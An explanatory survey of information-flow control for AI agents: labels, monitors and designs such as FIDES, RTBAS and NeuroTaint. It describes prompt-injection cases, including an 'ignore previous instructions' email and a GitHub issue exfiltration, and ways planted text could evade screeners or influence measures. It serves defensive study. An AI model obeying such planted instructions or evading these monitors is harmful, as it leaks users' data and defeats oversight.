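# Runtime information-flow control for the actions of AI agents

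## What is an information-flow policy, and how is it checked before an agent acts?

An information-flow policy is a rule about where data may go after someone has read it, or about which data may influence an action. Two examples are "the draft accounts may reach only the finance team" and "text from strangers may not cause a payment". Information-flow control is the family of methods for enforcing such rules. Software labels each piece of data, works out a label for everything derived from it, and checks the labels against the rule before the data leaves the system or takes effect. Computer scientists developed the method in the 1970s for shared computers and classified military files, and researchers now apply it to AI agents. An agent here is a language model run in a loop that can request actions, such as sending an email, and read their results.

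### The agent loop

A language model by itself only produces text. To make it an agent, a developer gives it a list of tools (functions that read mail, search the web, or edit files) along with the user's request. The model then replies with either ordinary text or a tool call, which is a structured request that names one tool and the arguments to pass to it. After a tool call, the application runs the tool, adds the result to the conversation, and sends the whole conversation back to the model, repeating this cycle until the model replies with ordinary text (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, 2025).

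Suppose a user asks an agent to summarize recent emails about a project and send the summary to her manager. On the first turn, the model requests the mail-reading tool, and the application fetches the emails. On the second, the model writes a summary and requests the mail-sending tool, with the summary as one of the arguments, and the application sends the message. On the third, the model outputs a message saying the job is done.

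The model only outputs text that describes a tool call, and the application then either executes the call or doesn't. Software outside the model, called the monitor, can therefore check each action before it takes effect.

A monitor protects only the routes that pass through it. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder listed complete mediation as a design principle, meaning that a system must check that every access to every object is authorized. An agent must therefore have no path to the outbox, the file system or the network that bypasses the monitor. Zhou and Zhang (2026), in *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents*, point out that this is harder to achieve than for ordinary software, because one agent action can affect several tools, other agents and outside services.

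The loop needs a check because it mixes instructions with data. The application gives the model a single string containing both the user's request and any emails or web pages the tools have returned, so the model can follow a sentence that an outsider has planted in an email as if it were an instruction, which is called prompt injection. Training and content filters make prompt injection less likely to succeed, but they are probabilistic and give no guarantee. Developers often require a person to approve each consequential action, but according to Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, this scales poorly, makes the approver less vigilant and takes away the autonomy that made the agent useful.

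### Why permission to read is not permission to send

The standard protection for files and mailboxes is access control, which gives each object a list of the people and programs that may open it. Once a permitted program has opened a file, the list does not restrict what the program does with the contents.

Sabelfeld and Myers (2003) point out in *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* that to keep a file confidential by access control alone, its owner would have to grant access only to programs that will never leak it. Access control cannot identify those programs. Saltzer and Schroeder had described controlling information after its release as "putting strings on information". Their example was a taxpayer who gives income figures to an adviser and wants to stop the adviser from passing them to a firm that prepares mailing lists. They knew of few systems that attempted this. One was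 ADEPT, which tracked the classification of everything a program had read and labeled its output with the highest of those classifications.

An agent widens this gap because it normally works with its user's permissions, so it can read whatever she can read and write to anyone she can write to. Each permission may be proper on its own, but the agent can cause harm by using them together, reading a document under one and mailing its contents under the other. Zhou and Zhang give the example of an assistant that prepares a report from company records. It reads the records, perhaps sends them to a hosted service for processing, passes a draft to a reviewing agent, and delivers the result to someone outside the company. Each step needs its own authorisation, even if the previous one was permitted.

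### Labels, their order and the join

The mathematics of information-flow policies comes from Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976). In this model, every object that can hold information (a file, a program variable, even a user) belongs to a security class. The relation A → B means that information in class A may flow into class B. A value computed from objects of classes A and B has the class A ⊕ B, and it may go into an object of class C only if A ⊕ B → C.

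Denning argued that the meaning of "flow" largely determines the structure of these parts. The relation has to be transitive. If the policy allowed A → B and B → C but not A → C, a program could still move information from A to C by copying it through B. The combined class must sit at or above both of its sources. Otherwise the system could let a program store a + b somewhere it may not store a, and the program could get around the ban by setting b to zero. The combined class must also be the lowest one with that property, because information that may enter C from A and from B separately can be combined once it is inside C. An operation that meets both conditions is a least upper bound, or join. With a finite set of classes and a lowest class, these conditions make the structure a lattice.

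A ⊕ B → C holds exactly when A → C and B → C both hold, so a single check on the combined label can replace separate checks on each source. *SPA* (2026), a design in which the agent plans before it acts, uses this fact for tool calls. Its monitor checks the combined label of all the arguments and blocks the call if any argument is not trusted enough for the tool.

In work on agents, a label usually has two parts. The confidentiality part specifies who may read the data. The simplest version has two levels, public and secret, with public below secret. A more useful version lists the permitted readers, and the join of two labels is then the intersection of their lists. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text that draws on both. A label with fewer readers is higher because it is more restrictive, and the label for data that anyone may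 read is at the bottom.

The integrity part of a label records who may have influenced the data. Sabelfeld and Myers credit Biba with the observation that integrity mirrors confidentiality, in that a confidentiality policy keeps information from reaching the wrong destinations and an integrity policy keeps out information from the wrong sources. "Trusted" is the low label and "untrusted" the high one, because untrusted data has restrictions on its use. Anything derived from at least one untrusted source is untrusted. If the label lists possible writers instead, the join is the union of the lists, because anyone who could have written to either source could have shaped the result. Since an integrity label records only influence, if a model misreads a wholly trusted spreadsheet, its wrong answer is still labeled "trusted".

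Together, the two parts order labels from trusted and public at the bottom to untrusted and secret at the top. Notation varies between designs. *APPA* (2026), for instance, expresses trust as a level. When combining two labels, it takes the minimum of their levels and intersects their lists of readers, which is the same rule with the trust scale reversed.

### Label, propagate, check

Microsoft divides enforcement into three steps. First, all data is labeled as it comes in. For example, a tool that fetches an email returns the text with labels that record who may read it and whether its source is trusted. Second, software propagates the labels, giving every derived piece of data the join of its sources' labels. Third, just before each tool call, the monitor compares the relevant labels with a policy and allows the call, blocks it or refers it to a person.

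For an agent, the second step depends on the context label, which is the join of the labels of everything in the model's current conversation. In the basic scheme from Costa and colleagues, the user's request normally enters as trusted and public. The scheme then joins each tool result's label to the context label and gives the resulting label to whatever the model writes next. Nobody can reliably tell which sentences in the conversation shaped a given reply, so the scheme deliberately makes the crude assumption that all of them did.

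Costa and colleagues build the third step on two basic policies. Under the integrity policy, a consequential tool call goes ahead only if the call and all its arguments are trusted. Under the confidentiality policy, a call that sends data through a channel (an email, a group chat, a public comment) goes ahead only if everyone who can read the channel is allowed to read the data.

### A leak with no attacker

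Microsoft gives an example that needs nothing beyond the confidentiality policy. Alex asks an agent to deal with the unanswered emails in his inbox. One is from Priya and contains a preview of the quarterly sales. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the sales but has no authorisation to see the figures early. The context label changes as the agent reads:

| Event | Readers of the new item | Readers of whatever the model writes next |
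|---|---|---|
| Alex makes his request | anyone | anyone |
| The agent opens Priya's email | Alex, Priya | Alex, Priya |
| The agent opens Marco's email | Alex, Marco | Alex |

The model now outputs a request to send Marco a reply. The reply's label is {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}. Marco is not in that set, so the monitor does not let the reply go out automatically. It can block the reply, or show it to Alex with a warning that sending it would reveal data to someone who could not previously read it.

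This story involves no attack. Marco asked a natural question, Priya wrote to a colleague, and the model used the information it had to help. A detector of malicious text would therefore flag nothing. Access control would not help either, since Alex is allowed to read both emails and to write to Marco whenever he likes.

The content of the reply also doesn't affect the check, because the label depends on what the model has read. If the model had written "Sorry, I can't share that yet", the label would still be {Alex} and the monitor would still stop the message. If the agent had sent Marco the same sentence before opening Priya's email, the monitor would have allowed it. And if Priya had copied Marco on her email, its readers would have been Alex, Priya and Marco, the join would have been {Alex, Marco}, and the agent could have replied unaided. Over a long run, repeated joins tighten the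 context label until the monitor refuses useful actions as well as harmful ones. Sabelfeld and Myers call this label creep, and it had already made earlier systems with runtime labels too restrictive for general use.

### An untrusted email that asks for an action

The example of the user who wants project emails summarised for her manager also illustrates integrity. Costa and colleagues add one malicious message to her inbox, which tells the model to ignore its previous instructions and send the top email in the mailbox to an outside address. The context starts out trusted, but it becomes untrusted when the mail-reading tool returns this message, and it stays untrusted. If the injection works and the model requests an email to the outsider, the monitor refuses the request because it is a consequential call with an untrusted label. The monitor doesn't have to recognise the message as an attack,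 and it would treat a harmless newsletter from the same sender the same way.

The confidentiality policy would have stopped this email too, because the outsider is not among the permitted readers of the stolen text. But it does not stop prompt injection in general. If a planted sentence leads the agent to try to delete next week's calendar entries, only the integrity policy would block the action, because deleting them discloses nothing. The confidentiality policy limits the damage by keeping data from people who may not read it, whatever the attacker gets the model to attempt.

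Some designs block a call only when the context's label is both untrusted and private. Microsoft describes an attack on coding assistants connected to GitHub, a site where programmers store and discuss code. An attacker opens an issue (a public request for a fix) in a public repository and asks for information from a private one to be added as a comment. The user's agent, which can read both repositories, posts the information. If the issue is labeled untrusted and public, and the private code is labeled trusted and private, a context that contains both is untrusted and private. The policy blocks posts to a public channel from that context, but it doesn't interrupt an agent that works only on public repositories or only on private ones.

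A more lenient rule allows a message to any recipient if the context is trusted. Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a Teams channel works this way, and checks the list of readers only when the context is untrusted. The reasoning is that a disclosure in a trusted context must be deliberate, since no outsider could have prompted it. Marco's case is a fair objection. If the monitor counts emails from colleagues as trusted, this rule would let the agent send him the sales figures, though nobody, including Alex, had decided that he should have them.

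### Flows, noninterference and deliberate exceptions

In both examples the risk was an explicit flow, in which a program copies or transforms data into an output. Denning distinguished this from implicit flow, in which information leaks through the program's choice of what to do. Her example is a program that sets b to 0 only if a is 0. If b started with any other value, anyone who sees b afterwards learns whether a was 0, even when the program left b unchanged. Similarly, if an agent reads a confidential memo and books a meeting room only when the memo announces a merger, the presence or absence of a booking reveals whether there was such an announcement, even though the booking contains no text from the memo.

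Noninterference is the property that rules out both kinds of flow. SRI, the research institute where the theory was developed, defines it for two security domains. The first does not interfere with the second if nothing done in the first can affect what is observed in the second afterwards. The usual test is whether an outsider could tell apart two runs that differ only in their secret inputs. For integrity, the runs differ only in their untrusted inputs, and the trusted outputs must be the same. This is a demanding standard, and the checks in the two email examples do not meet it by themselves.

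Useful work often requires exceptions to the labels. Declassification is a deliberate decision to let more readers see confidential data, as Alex does if he looks at the blocked reply and sends it anyway. Endorsement is a similar exception for integrity. It is a deliberate decision to treat untrusted data as trusted, as when a user confirms that an outside supplier's invoice is genuine and lets the agent pay it. Every exception also gives attackers something to exploit. In *Declassification*, Sabelfeld and Sands say the main worry is that an attacker will take control of the release mechanism and extract more than its designers meant to release.

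### What the attacker can and cannot do

Whether a check works depends on what the attacker controls. In the threat model of Costa and colleagues, the attacker can tamper with data that tools fetch from untrusted sources, such as incoming mail or web pages, and can observe the effects of some tool calls. The attacker cannot alter the user's request, the developer's instructions to the model, the tool descriptions, or the monitor and its labels, and cannot see what passes between the application and the model. Under these assumptions, a tool call that only reads data can still leak information. A web search returns public, untrusted text, but the request may show up in the visitor statistics of a site the attacker runs, so the monitor has to treat the search terms as outgoing data.

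Costa and colleagues list the model among the trusted parts of the configuration, meaning that nobody has tampered with it, but add that models make mistakes even when all their data is trusted. *APPA* does not trust the model at all in matters of policy and assumes that it may propose any tool call because of an injection, a hallucination or bad reasoning. The two positions lead to nearly the same monitor design, since neither relies on the model to judge whether a call is safe. Both designs also leave out timing, so their guarantees do not cover an attacker who learns something from how long the agent took to act. *APPA*'s guarantees also exclude faulty implementations of external tools.

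## How can a label follow data through a model that cannot be analysed like a program?

In a program, a line such as `total = price + tax` shows that `total` depends on `price` and `tax`. Software that reads the line can give `total` the join of their labels. It can also tell, before the program runs, that a variable called `password` elsewhere in the file does not affect `total`. When a language model chooses an agent's actions, the corresponding line is a call that takes in the whole conversation and returns text. That line shows only that the text depends on the conversation.

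### What changes when a model chooses the actions

A model's program is a long series of multiplications and additions, the same for every request, and a developer could track labels through it one operation at a time. The result would be correct but useless because, as *GIF* (Štorek, Holzer and colleagues, 2026) points out, any input token (a word or piece of a word) may influence any output token.

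An agent's behaviour in a particular run depends on the conversation and on the model's weights, the numbers fixed by training. Suppose an agent forwards every email that contains the word "urgent". If the agent were an ordinary program, an analyst could find the `if` statement responsible and label everything inside it as depending on the email. Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026) observe in *Ghost in the Agent* that an agent's branching happens invisibly within the weights.

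Content that a model reuses is also hard to track. Taint trackers for ordinary software, such as TaintDroid for smartphones, follow memory locations and registers, so a copied value keeps its label. But a model can put a fact from a web page into a summary or translation that shares no phrase with the page. It can also treat a sentence on the page as an instruction, because the page and the user's request arrive in the same string.

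The same conversation can also lead to different actions, because the model computes a probability for every possible next token and the software usually picks one at random using those probabilities. Changing one input and checking whether the output changes is therefore an unreliable test of influence, since the output may change anyway. Costa and colleagues set this problem aside in their proofs by assuming that the model is deterministic.

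JavaScript's `eval` function, which runs a string as code, poses a milder version of this problem. The code may not exist until the program is running, so nobody can analyse it in advance. Once the string exists, a runtime monitor can parse it, follow it statement by statement, and add the string's label to everything the code does, because whoever influenced the string also influenced those actions. A tool call also appears only at run time, and the monitor can read it before it is carried out. But the call comes out of the model without a label, whereas the string given to `eval` has one because the monitor tracked the statements that produced it.

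### The conservative answer

Costa and colleagues assume that anything in the model's context may have influenced its output, so they give everything the model writes the context's label. When the model replies with a tool call, their loop takes three steps.

1. The choice of tool gets the context label, and so does every argument.
2. The monitor checks the call against the policy and aborts the run if the check fails.
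3. If the check succeeds, the tool runs. Its result gets the join of the call's label, the arguments' labels and the labels of any stored data the tool may read. Any stored data the tool may write gets the same label.

The first step discards a lot of detail. An address that the user typed and the model copied exactly into the recipient field gets the same label as a phrase from a stranger's web page. The last step spreads untrusted labels to trusted data. If the agent reads a trusted file after an untrusted page, the file's contents are labelled untrusted, because the page may have influenced which file the agent opened.

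Suppose a user writes: "Tell Dana I'm coming on Monday, find the check-in time on the hotel's website, put it in my calendar, and send Dana the office address, 12 Mill Lane." The agent makes four calls to do this, and the policy requires consequential calls to be trusted.

| Call | Context before the call | Consequential? | Monitor | Context afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Message Dana: "I'm coming on Monday" | trusted | yes | allows | trusted |
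| 2. Fetch the hotel's web page | trusted | no | allows | untrusted |
| 3. Add "Check in, 3 pm" to the calendar | untrusted | yes | refuses | untrusted |
| 4. Message Dana: "12 Mill Lane" | untrusted | yes | refuses | untrusted |

The third call depends on the web page, but the fourth takes nothing from it and uses the same tool and recipient as the first call, which the monitor allowed. The published algorithm stops at the third call. If a developer changed it to report the refusal and continue, the fourth call would fail in the same way, and so would every later consequential call, because no step in the loop lowers the context label. If the agent had sent both messages before opening the page, only the calendar entry would have failed.

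This scheme is sound, meaning that a label never leaves out a source that had an influence. The model's reply can depend only on its inputs and the random choice of tokens, so the join of the labels on all its inputs covers every possible dependence. This holds regardless of how the model works or how well it resists prompt injection. The label of the next call will still be "untrusted" however an attacker words the hotel page.

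The drawback is label creep. In an ordinary program, a tainted value can stay in one variable while the program works with others. The basic agent loop is like a program with a single variable, the conversation, which every action reads and every result changes. Its label can only rise, and each new source may raise it. With a two-level integrity label, one untrusted source marks the whole conversation untrusted. After a long run, the label mostly reflects what has been in the conversation and may have little to do with what shaped the latest action.

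*Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (2026) gives a rough idea of how often always propagating the label can mark data unnecessarily. It covers applications whose ordinary code calls a language model, and its test set has 353 pairs, each made up of a prompt input and a sensitive operation later in the code. The input did not reach the operation in 243 pairs, so always propagating the label would have been wrong for 69 per cent of the pairs. The pairs came from 62 files that all contained a sensitive operation, and none was an agent's conversation, so the share for agents could be quite different.

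*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes label propagation through language models as an open problem. For now, one can only assume that the output carries the union of the input labels. Developers can avoid some of the resulting label creep by keeping untrusted text out of the conversation and giving the model only the name of a variable that holds it. Other researchers leave the text in and try to work out which parts of it influenced the output.

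### Regenerating the answer from fewer inputs

Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2025), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, look for the inputs that influenced a response and then regenerate the response from those inputs alone. If the inputs have labels ℓ₁ to ℓₙ, the conservative label for the response is the join of all of them. A response generated from a subset needs only the join of that subset's labels. They aim to find a subset that has a less restrictive label and still gives a good answer.

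In the hotel example, the model can write the second message to Dana without the web page, so the regenerated call would be trusted and the monitor would allow it. The calendar entry needs the check-in time, which only the page provides, so the model has to keep the page in its context and the monitor would still refuse that call.

Six of the paper's authors also worked on the planning loop described above. Costa and colleagues report that the regenerated responses are about as useful as the originals, and that their own framework could accommodate the method, though they leave it out for simplicity. The harder problem is the amount of computation, because n inputs have 2ⁿ subsets to try. *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025), which proposes a rival design, says that even the optimised version needs exponentially more model calls as the lattice gains levels, with 16 extra calls for four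 levels and 64 for six. It adds that the method labels only a single response and does not specify what happens to labels afterwards, so it does not yet cover an agent that calls tools.

Regeneration gives the method some protection against its own mistakes. If the analysis wrongly concludes that a malicious document had no influence, the software generates a new response without that document, so an attacker gains little by making a document look irrelevant. But the software uses every input to choose which ones to keep, so a document might still influence the outcome through that choice. RTBAS has the same gap, and it is easier to see there how an attacker could exploit it.

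### Screening and masking in RTBAS

Zhong and colleagues replace the search over subsets with a single judgment, made by a component called a dependency screener. They divide the conversation into regions, each with its own label. Before the model writes its next message, the screener picks out the regions that message depends on. The software joins the labels of those regions and blanks out every region whose label is not at or below the join. The model writes its message from what remains, and any tool call it makes carries the joined label. If the policy forbids the call, the system asks the user.

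They built two screeners. One is a second language model that reads the conversation, with its regions marked, and lists the relevant ones. The other uses attention scores, which estimate how much worse a model would predict each output word if a given input word were missing. A small neural network turns the scores for each region into a yes or no. This screener needs a message to analyse, so the agent's model drafts one from the full conversation, then writes it again after masking.

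The attention scores indicate dependence, but not reliably. Zhong and colleagues collected 3,424 pairs of an input and a tool call from agent runs and labeled each pair as dependent or independent. Between 74 and 86 per cent of the scores for independent pairs were below 0.2, but so were 14 per cent of the scores for dependent pairs with agents running on GPT-4o and 44 per cent with agents running on Claude. The trained classifier was correct on 81 per cent of the test data.

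The RTBAS tests for prompt injection used AgentDojo, a test suite of office, travel, banking and chat tasks with planted instructions, with GPT-4o as the agent's model. Across 629 attack cases, RTBAS stopped every attack that broke the policy. The tracking missed one attack because it was in text written by the user, which was labelled as trusted. Compared with an undefended agent under attack, the share of tasks completed fell by less than 1 per cent with the model screener and by 3 per cent with the attention screener. Without attacks, it fell by 10 and 7.4 per cent respectively. On the banking tasks, both screeners roughly doubled the time and the number of tokens.

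The agent completed a much smaller share of the chat tasks, 22 per cent with the model screener and 33 per cent with the attention screener. Many of these tasks involve reading an untrusted website and acting on what it says, and the software skipped forbidden calls instead of asking a user. Better screening would not have helped with such tasks, because their actions depend on untrusted text and even a perfectly accurate label would be "untrusted".

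For privacy, Zhong and colleagues wrote 37 cases about shopping, payments and flight booking, and marked by hand which tool calls would disclose private data. Asking the user every time led to needless questions in 11 of the 37 cases. The model screener reduced that to 3 and the attention screener to 6, but each failed to ask in 4 cases where it should have. (The paper's text swaps the definitions of the two error rates, but its table and discussion fit the reading given here.) The computed label named exactly the right kinds of private data for 70 per cent of tool calls with the model screener and 57 per cent with the attention screener. Assuming that every secret in the conversation flows into every call gives about the same result as the attention screener.

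Zhong and colleagues argue that even at this error rate, wrong verdicts cannot compromise security, because the software blanks out anything the label does not cover. If the screener overlooks a secret, the model never sees it and may fail at the task as a result. The argument works well for data that an action copies or uses, and it also covers a planted instruction written to look irrelevant.

It does not quite cover influence through the masking itself. The screener reads the untrusted text, so that text may affect which label the screener produces. The simplest lattice has only four labels, so an attacker can choose between at most four versions of the conversation at each step, but the choice can matter. Suppose a private note from the finance team says not to pay a supplier yet, and the user asks the agent to pay this month's invoices. If a planted sentence leads the screener to treat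 the note as irrelevant, the software may use the label "trusted and public" and blank out the note because it is private. The planted sentence is blanked out too, but only after it has affected the label. The model then requests the payment without having seen the warning, and the monitor allows it as a trusted call. The AgentDojo attacks aim to make an agent misuse its tools, and Zhong and colleagues do not report any tests with text written to mislead the screener.

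### Measuring influence with Geometric Information Flow

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests replacing yes-or-no labels with soft labels that record how much information an output carries about each labeled input. Štorek and colleagues at Columbia University developed one such measure, Geometric Information Flow.

The model turns each input token into a list of numbers, called its embedding. Suppose we add a small random disturbance U to the embeddings of one stretch of the input, such as a sentence in an applicant's CV, and keep everything else fixed. If Y is the next token the model produces, the flow from the sentence to Y is the mutual information I(U; Y), which measures how much one could learn about U by seeing Y. It is zero exactly when Y is independent of U.

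Calculating this exactly would mean averaging over every possible disturbance, so Štorek and colleagues approximate it with three matrices. J records how far the model's internal state moves when the embedding moves slightly. W turns the internal state into a score for every token in the vocabulary. F records how far the next-token probabilities p move when those scores change, and equals diag(p) − ppᵀ. They combine the three as

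M = Jᵀ Wᵀ F W J

and define the flow as ½ log det(I + τM), where τ sets the size of the disturbance. If λ₁, λ₂ and so on are the eigenvalues of M, this equals ½ Σ log(1 + τλᵢ). Each eigenvalue measures how sensitive the output is to movement in one direction, so the flow is large if nudging the sentence in some direction changes the output a lot. For speed, their system estimates the sum of the eigenvalues from a few random probes and ranks the input tokens by the result.

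In their example, an applicant's CV contains a hidden instruction to recommend the applicant at a salary of $200,000, and the agent obeys. The measure attributes 82 bits of flow to the hidden instruction, 27 to the employer's own hiring criteria and 16 to the rest of the text. A conservative label would have recorded only that a CV was present.

Štorek and colleagues give a computer-checked proof that the true mutual information exceeds their figure by at most an error that shrinks faster than τ as τ approaches zero. This guarantee covers only tiny disturbances around one fixed prompt. An attacker replaces whole sentences, and the model can behave very differently when the wording changes that much.

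Under this formula, a strong influence could get a low figure. When the model has only two possible tokens, with probabilities p and 1 − p, F shrinks in proportion to p(1 − p). This product is 0.25 at p = 0.5 but about 0.001 at p = 0.999, which is 250 times smaller. So if a planted instruction makes the model almost certain of the attacker's address, small changes to the instruction no longer alter the output much, and the measured flow falls even though the instruction determined the result. Ranking the inputs helps because the shrinkage affects all of them, but some input will always rank first, so a person or another mechanism must still decide whether that input had a harmful effect.

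The main test covered six open-weight models (models whose weights anyone can download) and three benchmarks. AgentDojo and MSB contain prompt injections, and AgentDAM tests whether web-browsing agents disclose private data. For each tool call, Štorek and colleagues took the top-ranked input tokens and calculated what fraction belonged to the planted instruction or the private data. They measured how well this fraction separated runs with a violation from runs without one. The figures below give the chance that a randomly chosen run with a violation scores higher than a randomly chosen run without one, so 0.5 is no better than guessing. The last two columns are for their own version of the attention method from RTBAS.

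| Benchmark | Geometric flow, top 5 tokens | Geometric flow, top 50 | Attention, top 5 | Attention, top 50 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 0.75 | 0.91 | 0.56 | 0.84 |
| MSB | 0.84 | 0.92 | 0.53 | 0.76 |
| AgentDAM | 0.64 | 0.75 | 0.54 | 0.57 |

The geometric measure clearly does better than attention, though it is much weaker on privacy than on prompt injection. The test also favours both methods, because the scoring relied on the benchmark's own record of which tokens were malicious or private, which a deployed monitor would not have. A simpler method, which ranks tokens by their effect on the score of the token the model produced, came within 0.03 of the geometric measure in every cell of the table. The main benefit of the extra mathematics therefore seems to be a formal guarantee rather than better accuracy.

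In a version that needs no such record, Štorek and colleagues show a language model only the one to three most influential stretches of text and ask it to allow or deny the action. Its verdicts were between 0.97 and 1.22 times as good as those of the same model reading the whole run. When shown one stretch, it used 63 to 73 per cent fewer tokens on the two injection benchmarks. The influence calculation can also use a different model from the agent's. When they used a 0.6-billion-parameter model to analyse runs of a 120-billion-parameter model, no accuracy figure changed by more than 0.9 percentage points.

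Using a small public model helps defenders who cannot see inside a commercial one, but it may also help attackers, who could run the same calculation and reword an instruction until its score dropped. Štorek and colleagues did not test this attack. Their system also leaves the text it ranks as unimportant in the conversation, so an instruction it overlooks can still influence the model. The final verdict comes from a language model that reads the suspicious text.

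### Labels with confidence scores in NeuroTaint

Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint, which reconstructs influences from an agent's log after the run has finished. A developer can use it to find out that a web page led to an email, but only after the email has been sent. Each NeuroTaint label contains an identifier, the source of the data and a confidence score between 0 and 1.

Whenever the log contains a sensitive tool call, NeuroTaint checks each earlier source that could have reached it. It first looks for copied content, using tests that range from exact to loose:

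- a unique random code that NeuroTaint attached to the source when the agent read it;
- a sequence of shared characters amounting to at least 15 per cent of the shorter text;
- similarity of meaning, as measured by a separate language-processing model;
- the same comparison of meaning against short chunks of the source, for cases where one malicious paragraph sits in a long page.

If all of these fail, NeuroTaint checks whether the source influenced the decision. It replaces the source with a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found", and asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call. If the answer is no, it records an influence.

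The confidence scores are produced in different ways. Finding the random code gives a score of 1, and the tests of wording and meaning give a degree of similarity. For an influence on a decision, the score is the confidence that the judging model assigns to its own answer. Cai and colleagues warn that this is not a calibrated probability, so a policy that allowed calls with a score below, say, 0.3 would have no fixed error rate.

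Cai and colleagues tested NeuroTaint on TaintBench, a set of 400 scenarios they wrote themselves. In half of them, a source influences the agent. NeuroTaint found 187 of these 200 influences and raised 16 false alarms. Ten of the 13 misses involved text that the agent had paraphrased repeatedly or later recalled from memory, and the other three involved a source that changed the agent's decision but left little trace in the tool call. The false alarms mostly came from outputs that happened to share the source's topic, or that the model could have written from general knowledge.

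By comparison, FIDES, the full system from Costa and colleagues, found 108 of the influences in the same test, missed 92 and raised 106 false alarms. The misses are strange because a context label marks every call that follows an untrusted source in the same session, so it should raise many false alarms and miss almost nothing. The version of FIDES in this test also flagged nothing on four of the twenty agent frameworks. It seems to have looked for known paths between tools, so the comparison is weak evidence about the scheme in which every reply inherits the whole context label.

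An attacker has several ways to get past NeuroTaint. Its scope excludes attacks hidden in images and tricks such as swapping letters for lookalike characters. Its misses show that repeated paraphrasing can push a real influence below the thresholds, and the judging model reads text that the attacker may have written. NeuroTaint also has no equivalent of masking, which would make a miss harmless.

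### What each kind of mistake costs

If a method that estimates influence misses one, the monitor may allow an action that the policy should block, such as a payment caused by a stranger's text. If the method reports an influence that was not there, the monitor refuses a harmless action or interrupts the user. Adjusting the method's thresholds reduces one kind of mistake but increases the other. Cai and colleagues got more false alarms when they lowered NeuroTaint's thresholds and more misses when they raised them.

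The two rates mean different things when someone is attacking the system. NeuroTaint missed 6.5 per cent of the influences in TaintBench, but that is an average over scenarios that its developers chose. An attacker needs only one wording that the method misses, and can search for it in private and then put it in any number of emails. A low miss rate on a benchmark therefore cannot replace the guarantee of the conservative label. Masking preserves much of that guarantee by hiding from the model whatever the estimate left out, so an omission mainly reduces how well the model does the task.

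Individual false influences are less dangerous, but they accumulate. In many designs, each adds a request for confirmation, and frequent requests make users less vigilant. Labels that are far too cautious can therefore lead users to approve actions that the policy was meant to stop.

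## How can an agent use untrusted data without restricting everything it does next?

In the basic agent loop, one untrusted web page makes the whole conversation untrusted, because the loop shows the page to the model that chooses the actions. Many tasks don't require the model to read the untrusted text. To forward an email, an agent needs to know which email to send and who should get it, but not what it says. The software can keep the text out of the conversation and let the model refer to it by name.

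### A planning model and a quarantined model

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, the software developer Simon Willison (2023) proposed building an agent from two models and a controller, which is ordinary software. The planning model, which he calls the privileged model, receives the user's request and chooses the tool calls, but never reads untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools, because Willison assumes that it may obey an attacker at any moment. The controller runs the tools, stores their results and passes data between the models.

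Suppose the user asks for a summary of her latest email.

1. The planning model requests the email and names the result $VAR1.
2. The controller fetches the email and stores it under that name, without showing the text to the planning model.
3. The planning model requests a call to the quarantined model with the instruction "Summarize this: $VAR1".
4. The controller replaces the name with the email's text, runs the quarantined model and stores its answer as $VAR2. It tells the planning model only that the summary is ready.
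5. The planning model writes a reply that contains the name $VAR2, and the controller fills in the summary on the user's screen.

If the email contains an order to delete the mailbox, only the quarantined model reads the order, and it has no tool for deleting anything. But a planted instruction could make the quarantined model copy the order into its summary, so the controller has to keep the summary from the planning model too. Willison allows one exception, for when the quarantined model sorts text into a fixed set of categories. The controller can then check that the output is exactly one of those categories and pass it to the planning model.

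Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and one programming mistake that lets untrusted text through to the planning model would undo the protection. An attacker can also use the text on the screen to trick the user, for example by telling her to paste a block of encoded text into a website to see a funny picture, when the block contains her private data.

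The pattern also has no labels to record who wrote the contents of $VAR2 or who may read them, and the planning model can pass the variable to any tool. Two later designs, CaMeL and FIDES, add such labels. In CaMeL, the planning model writes a program that software then checks. Willison has acknowledged that CaMeL addresses a flaw in his proposal. FIDES, by Costa and colleagues, keeps the loop in which the model chooses one call at a time.

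### Variables with their own labels

FIDES hides only what would raise the context label. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares each part's label with the context label. If the part's label is at or below the context label, FIDES adds the part to the conversation. Otherwise, it stores the part and its label in a new variable and adds only the variable's name. The context label stays the same in both cases.

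The comparison works field by field. If an email's date is trusted but its subject and body are not, the planning model receives the real date, with variable names in place of the subject and body. It can then pick out last week's emails without reading the untrusted text.

The planning model can use variable names as arguments when it requests a tool call. The software replaces each name with the stored contents and their label, and the monitor then checks the call. An argument that came from a variable has that variable's label instead of the context label it would have in the basic loop.

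Costa and colleagues describe a run in which a user asks the agent to find the chat channel with the fewest messages and add Alice to it. The planning model receives the channel names and messages only as variables. It requests the messages in each channel, finds one empty list, and adds Alice to that channel by passing the variable that holds its name. The model never reads a message, but it has access to the number of messages. Anyone who can post in a channel can change that number, so a developer who labels the number "trusted" is making an assumption about who can post.

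The planning model can use what is in a variable in two ways. It can open the variable, which adds the contents to the conversation and raises the context label. Or it can send a question and some variables to a quarantined model. The software stores the answer in a new variable, whose label is the join of the context label and the labels of all the variables sent.

This join also protects secrets. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, analyses a worst case in which the attacker controls how the quarantined model's answer depends on everything in the query, including secrets. If a query contains both a stranger's email and the user's account number, the answer might contain the account number. Under FIDES's rule, only people allowed to read the account number may read the answer, so a confidentiality check would stop the agent from sending it to the stranger.

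The same mechanism solves Alex's problem with his inbox, because the agent can have a quarantined model draft the replies to Priya and Marco separately. The reply to Priya is labeled as readable by Alex and Priya, and the reply to Marco as readable by Alex and Marco, so the monitor allows both. The reply to Marco can't reveal the sales figures, because the model call that wrote it never received them. This follows from the design, but Costa and colleagues created variables only for untrusted data in their tests, not for confidential data.

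### Why a message may be untrusted when its recipient may not

The strict integrity policy requires every argument of a consequential call to be trusted. If each argument has its own label, a policy can set different requirements for each. For a tool that sends messages, Costa and colleagues suggest requiring the choice of tool and the recipient to be trusted, but allowing an untrusted body, such as the results of a web search.

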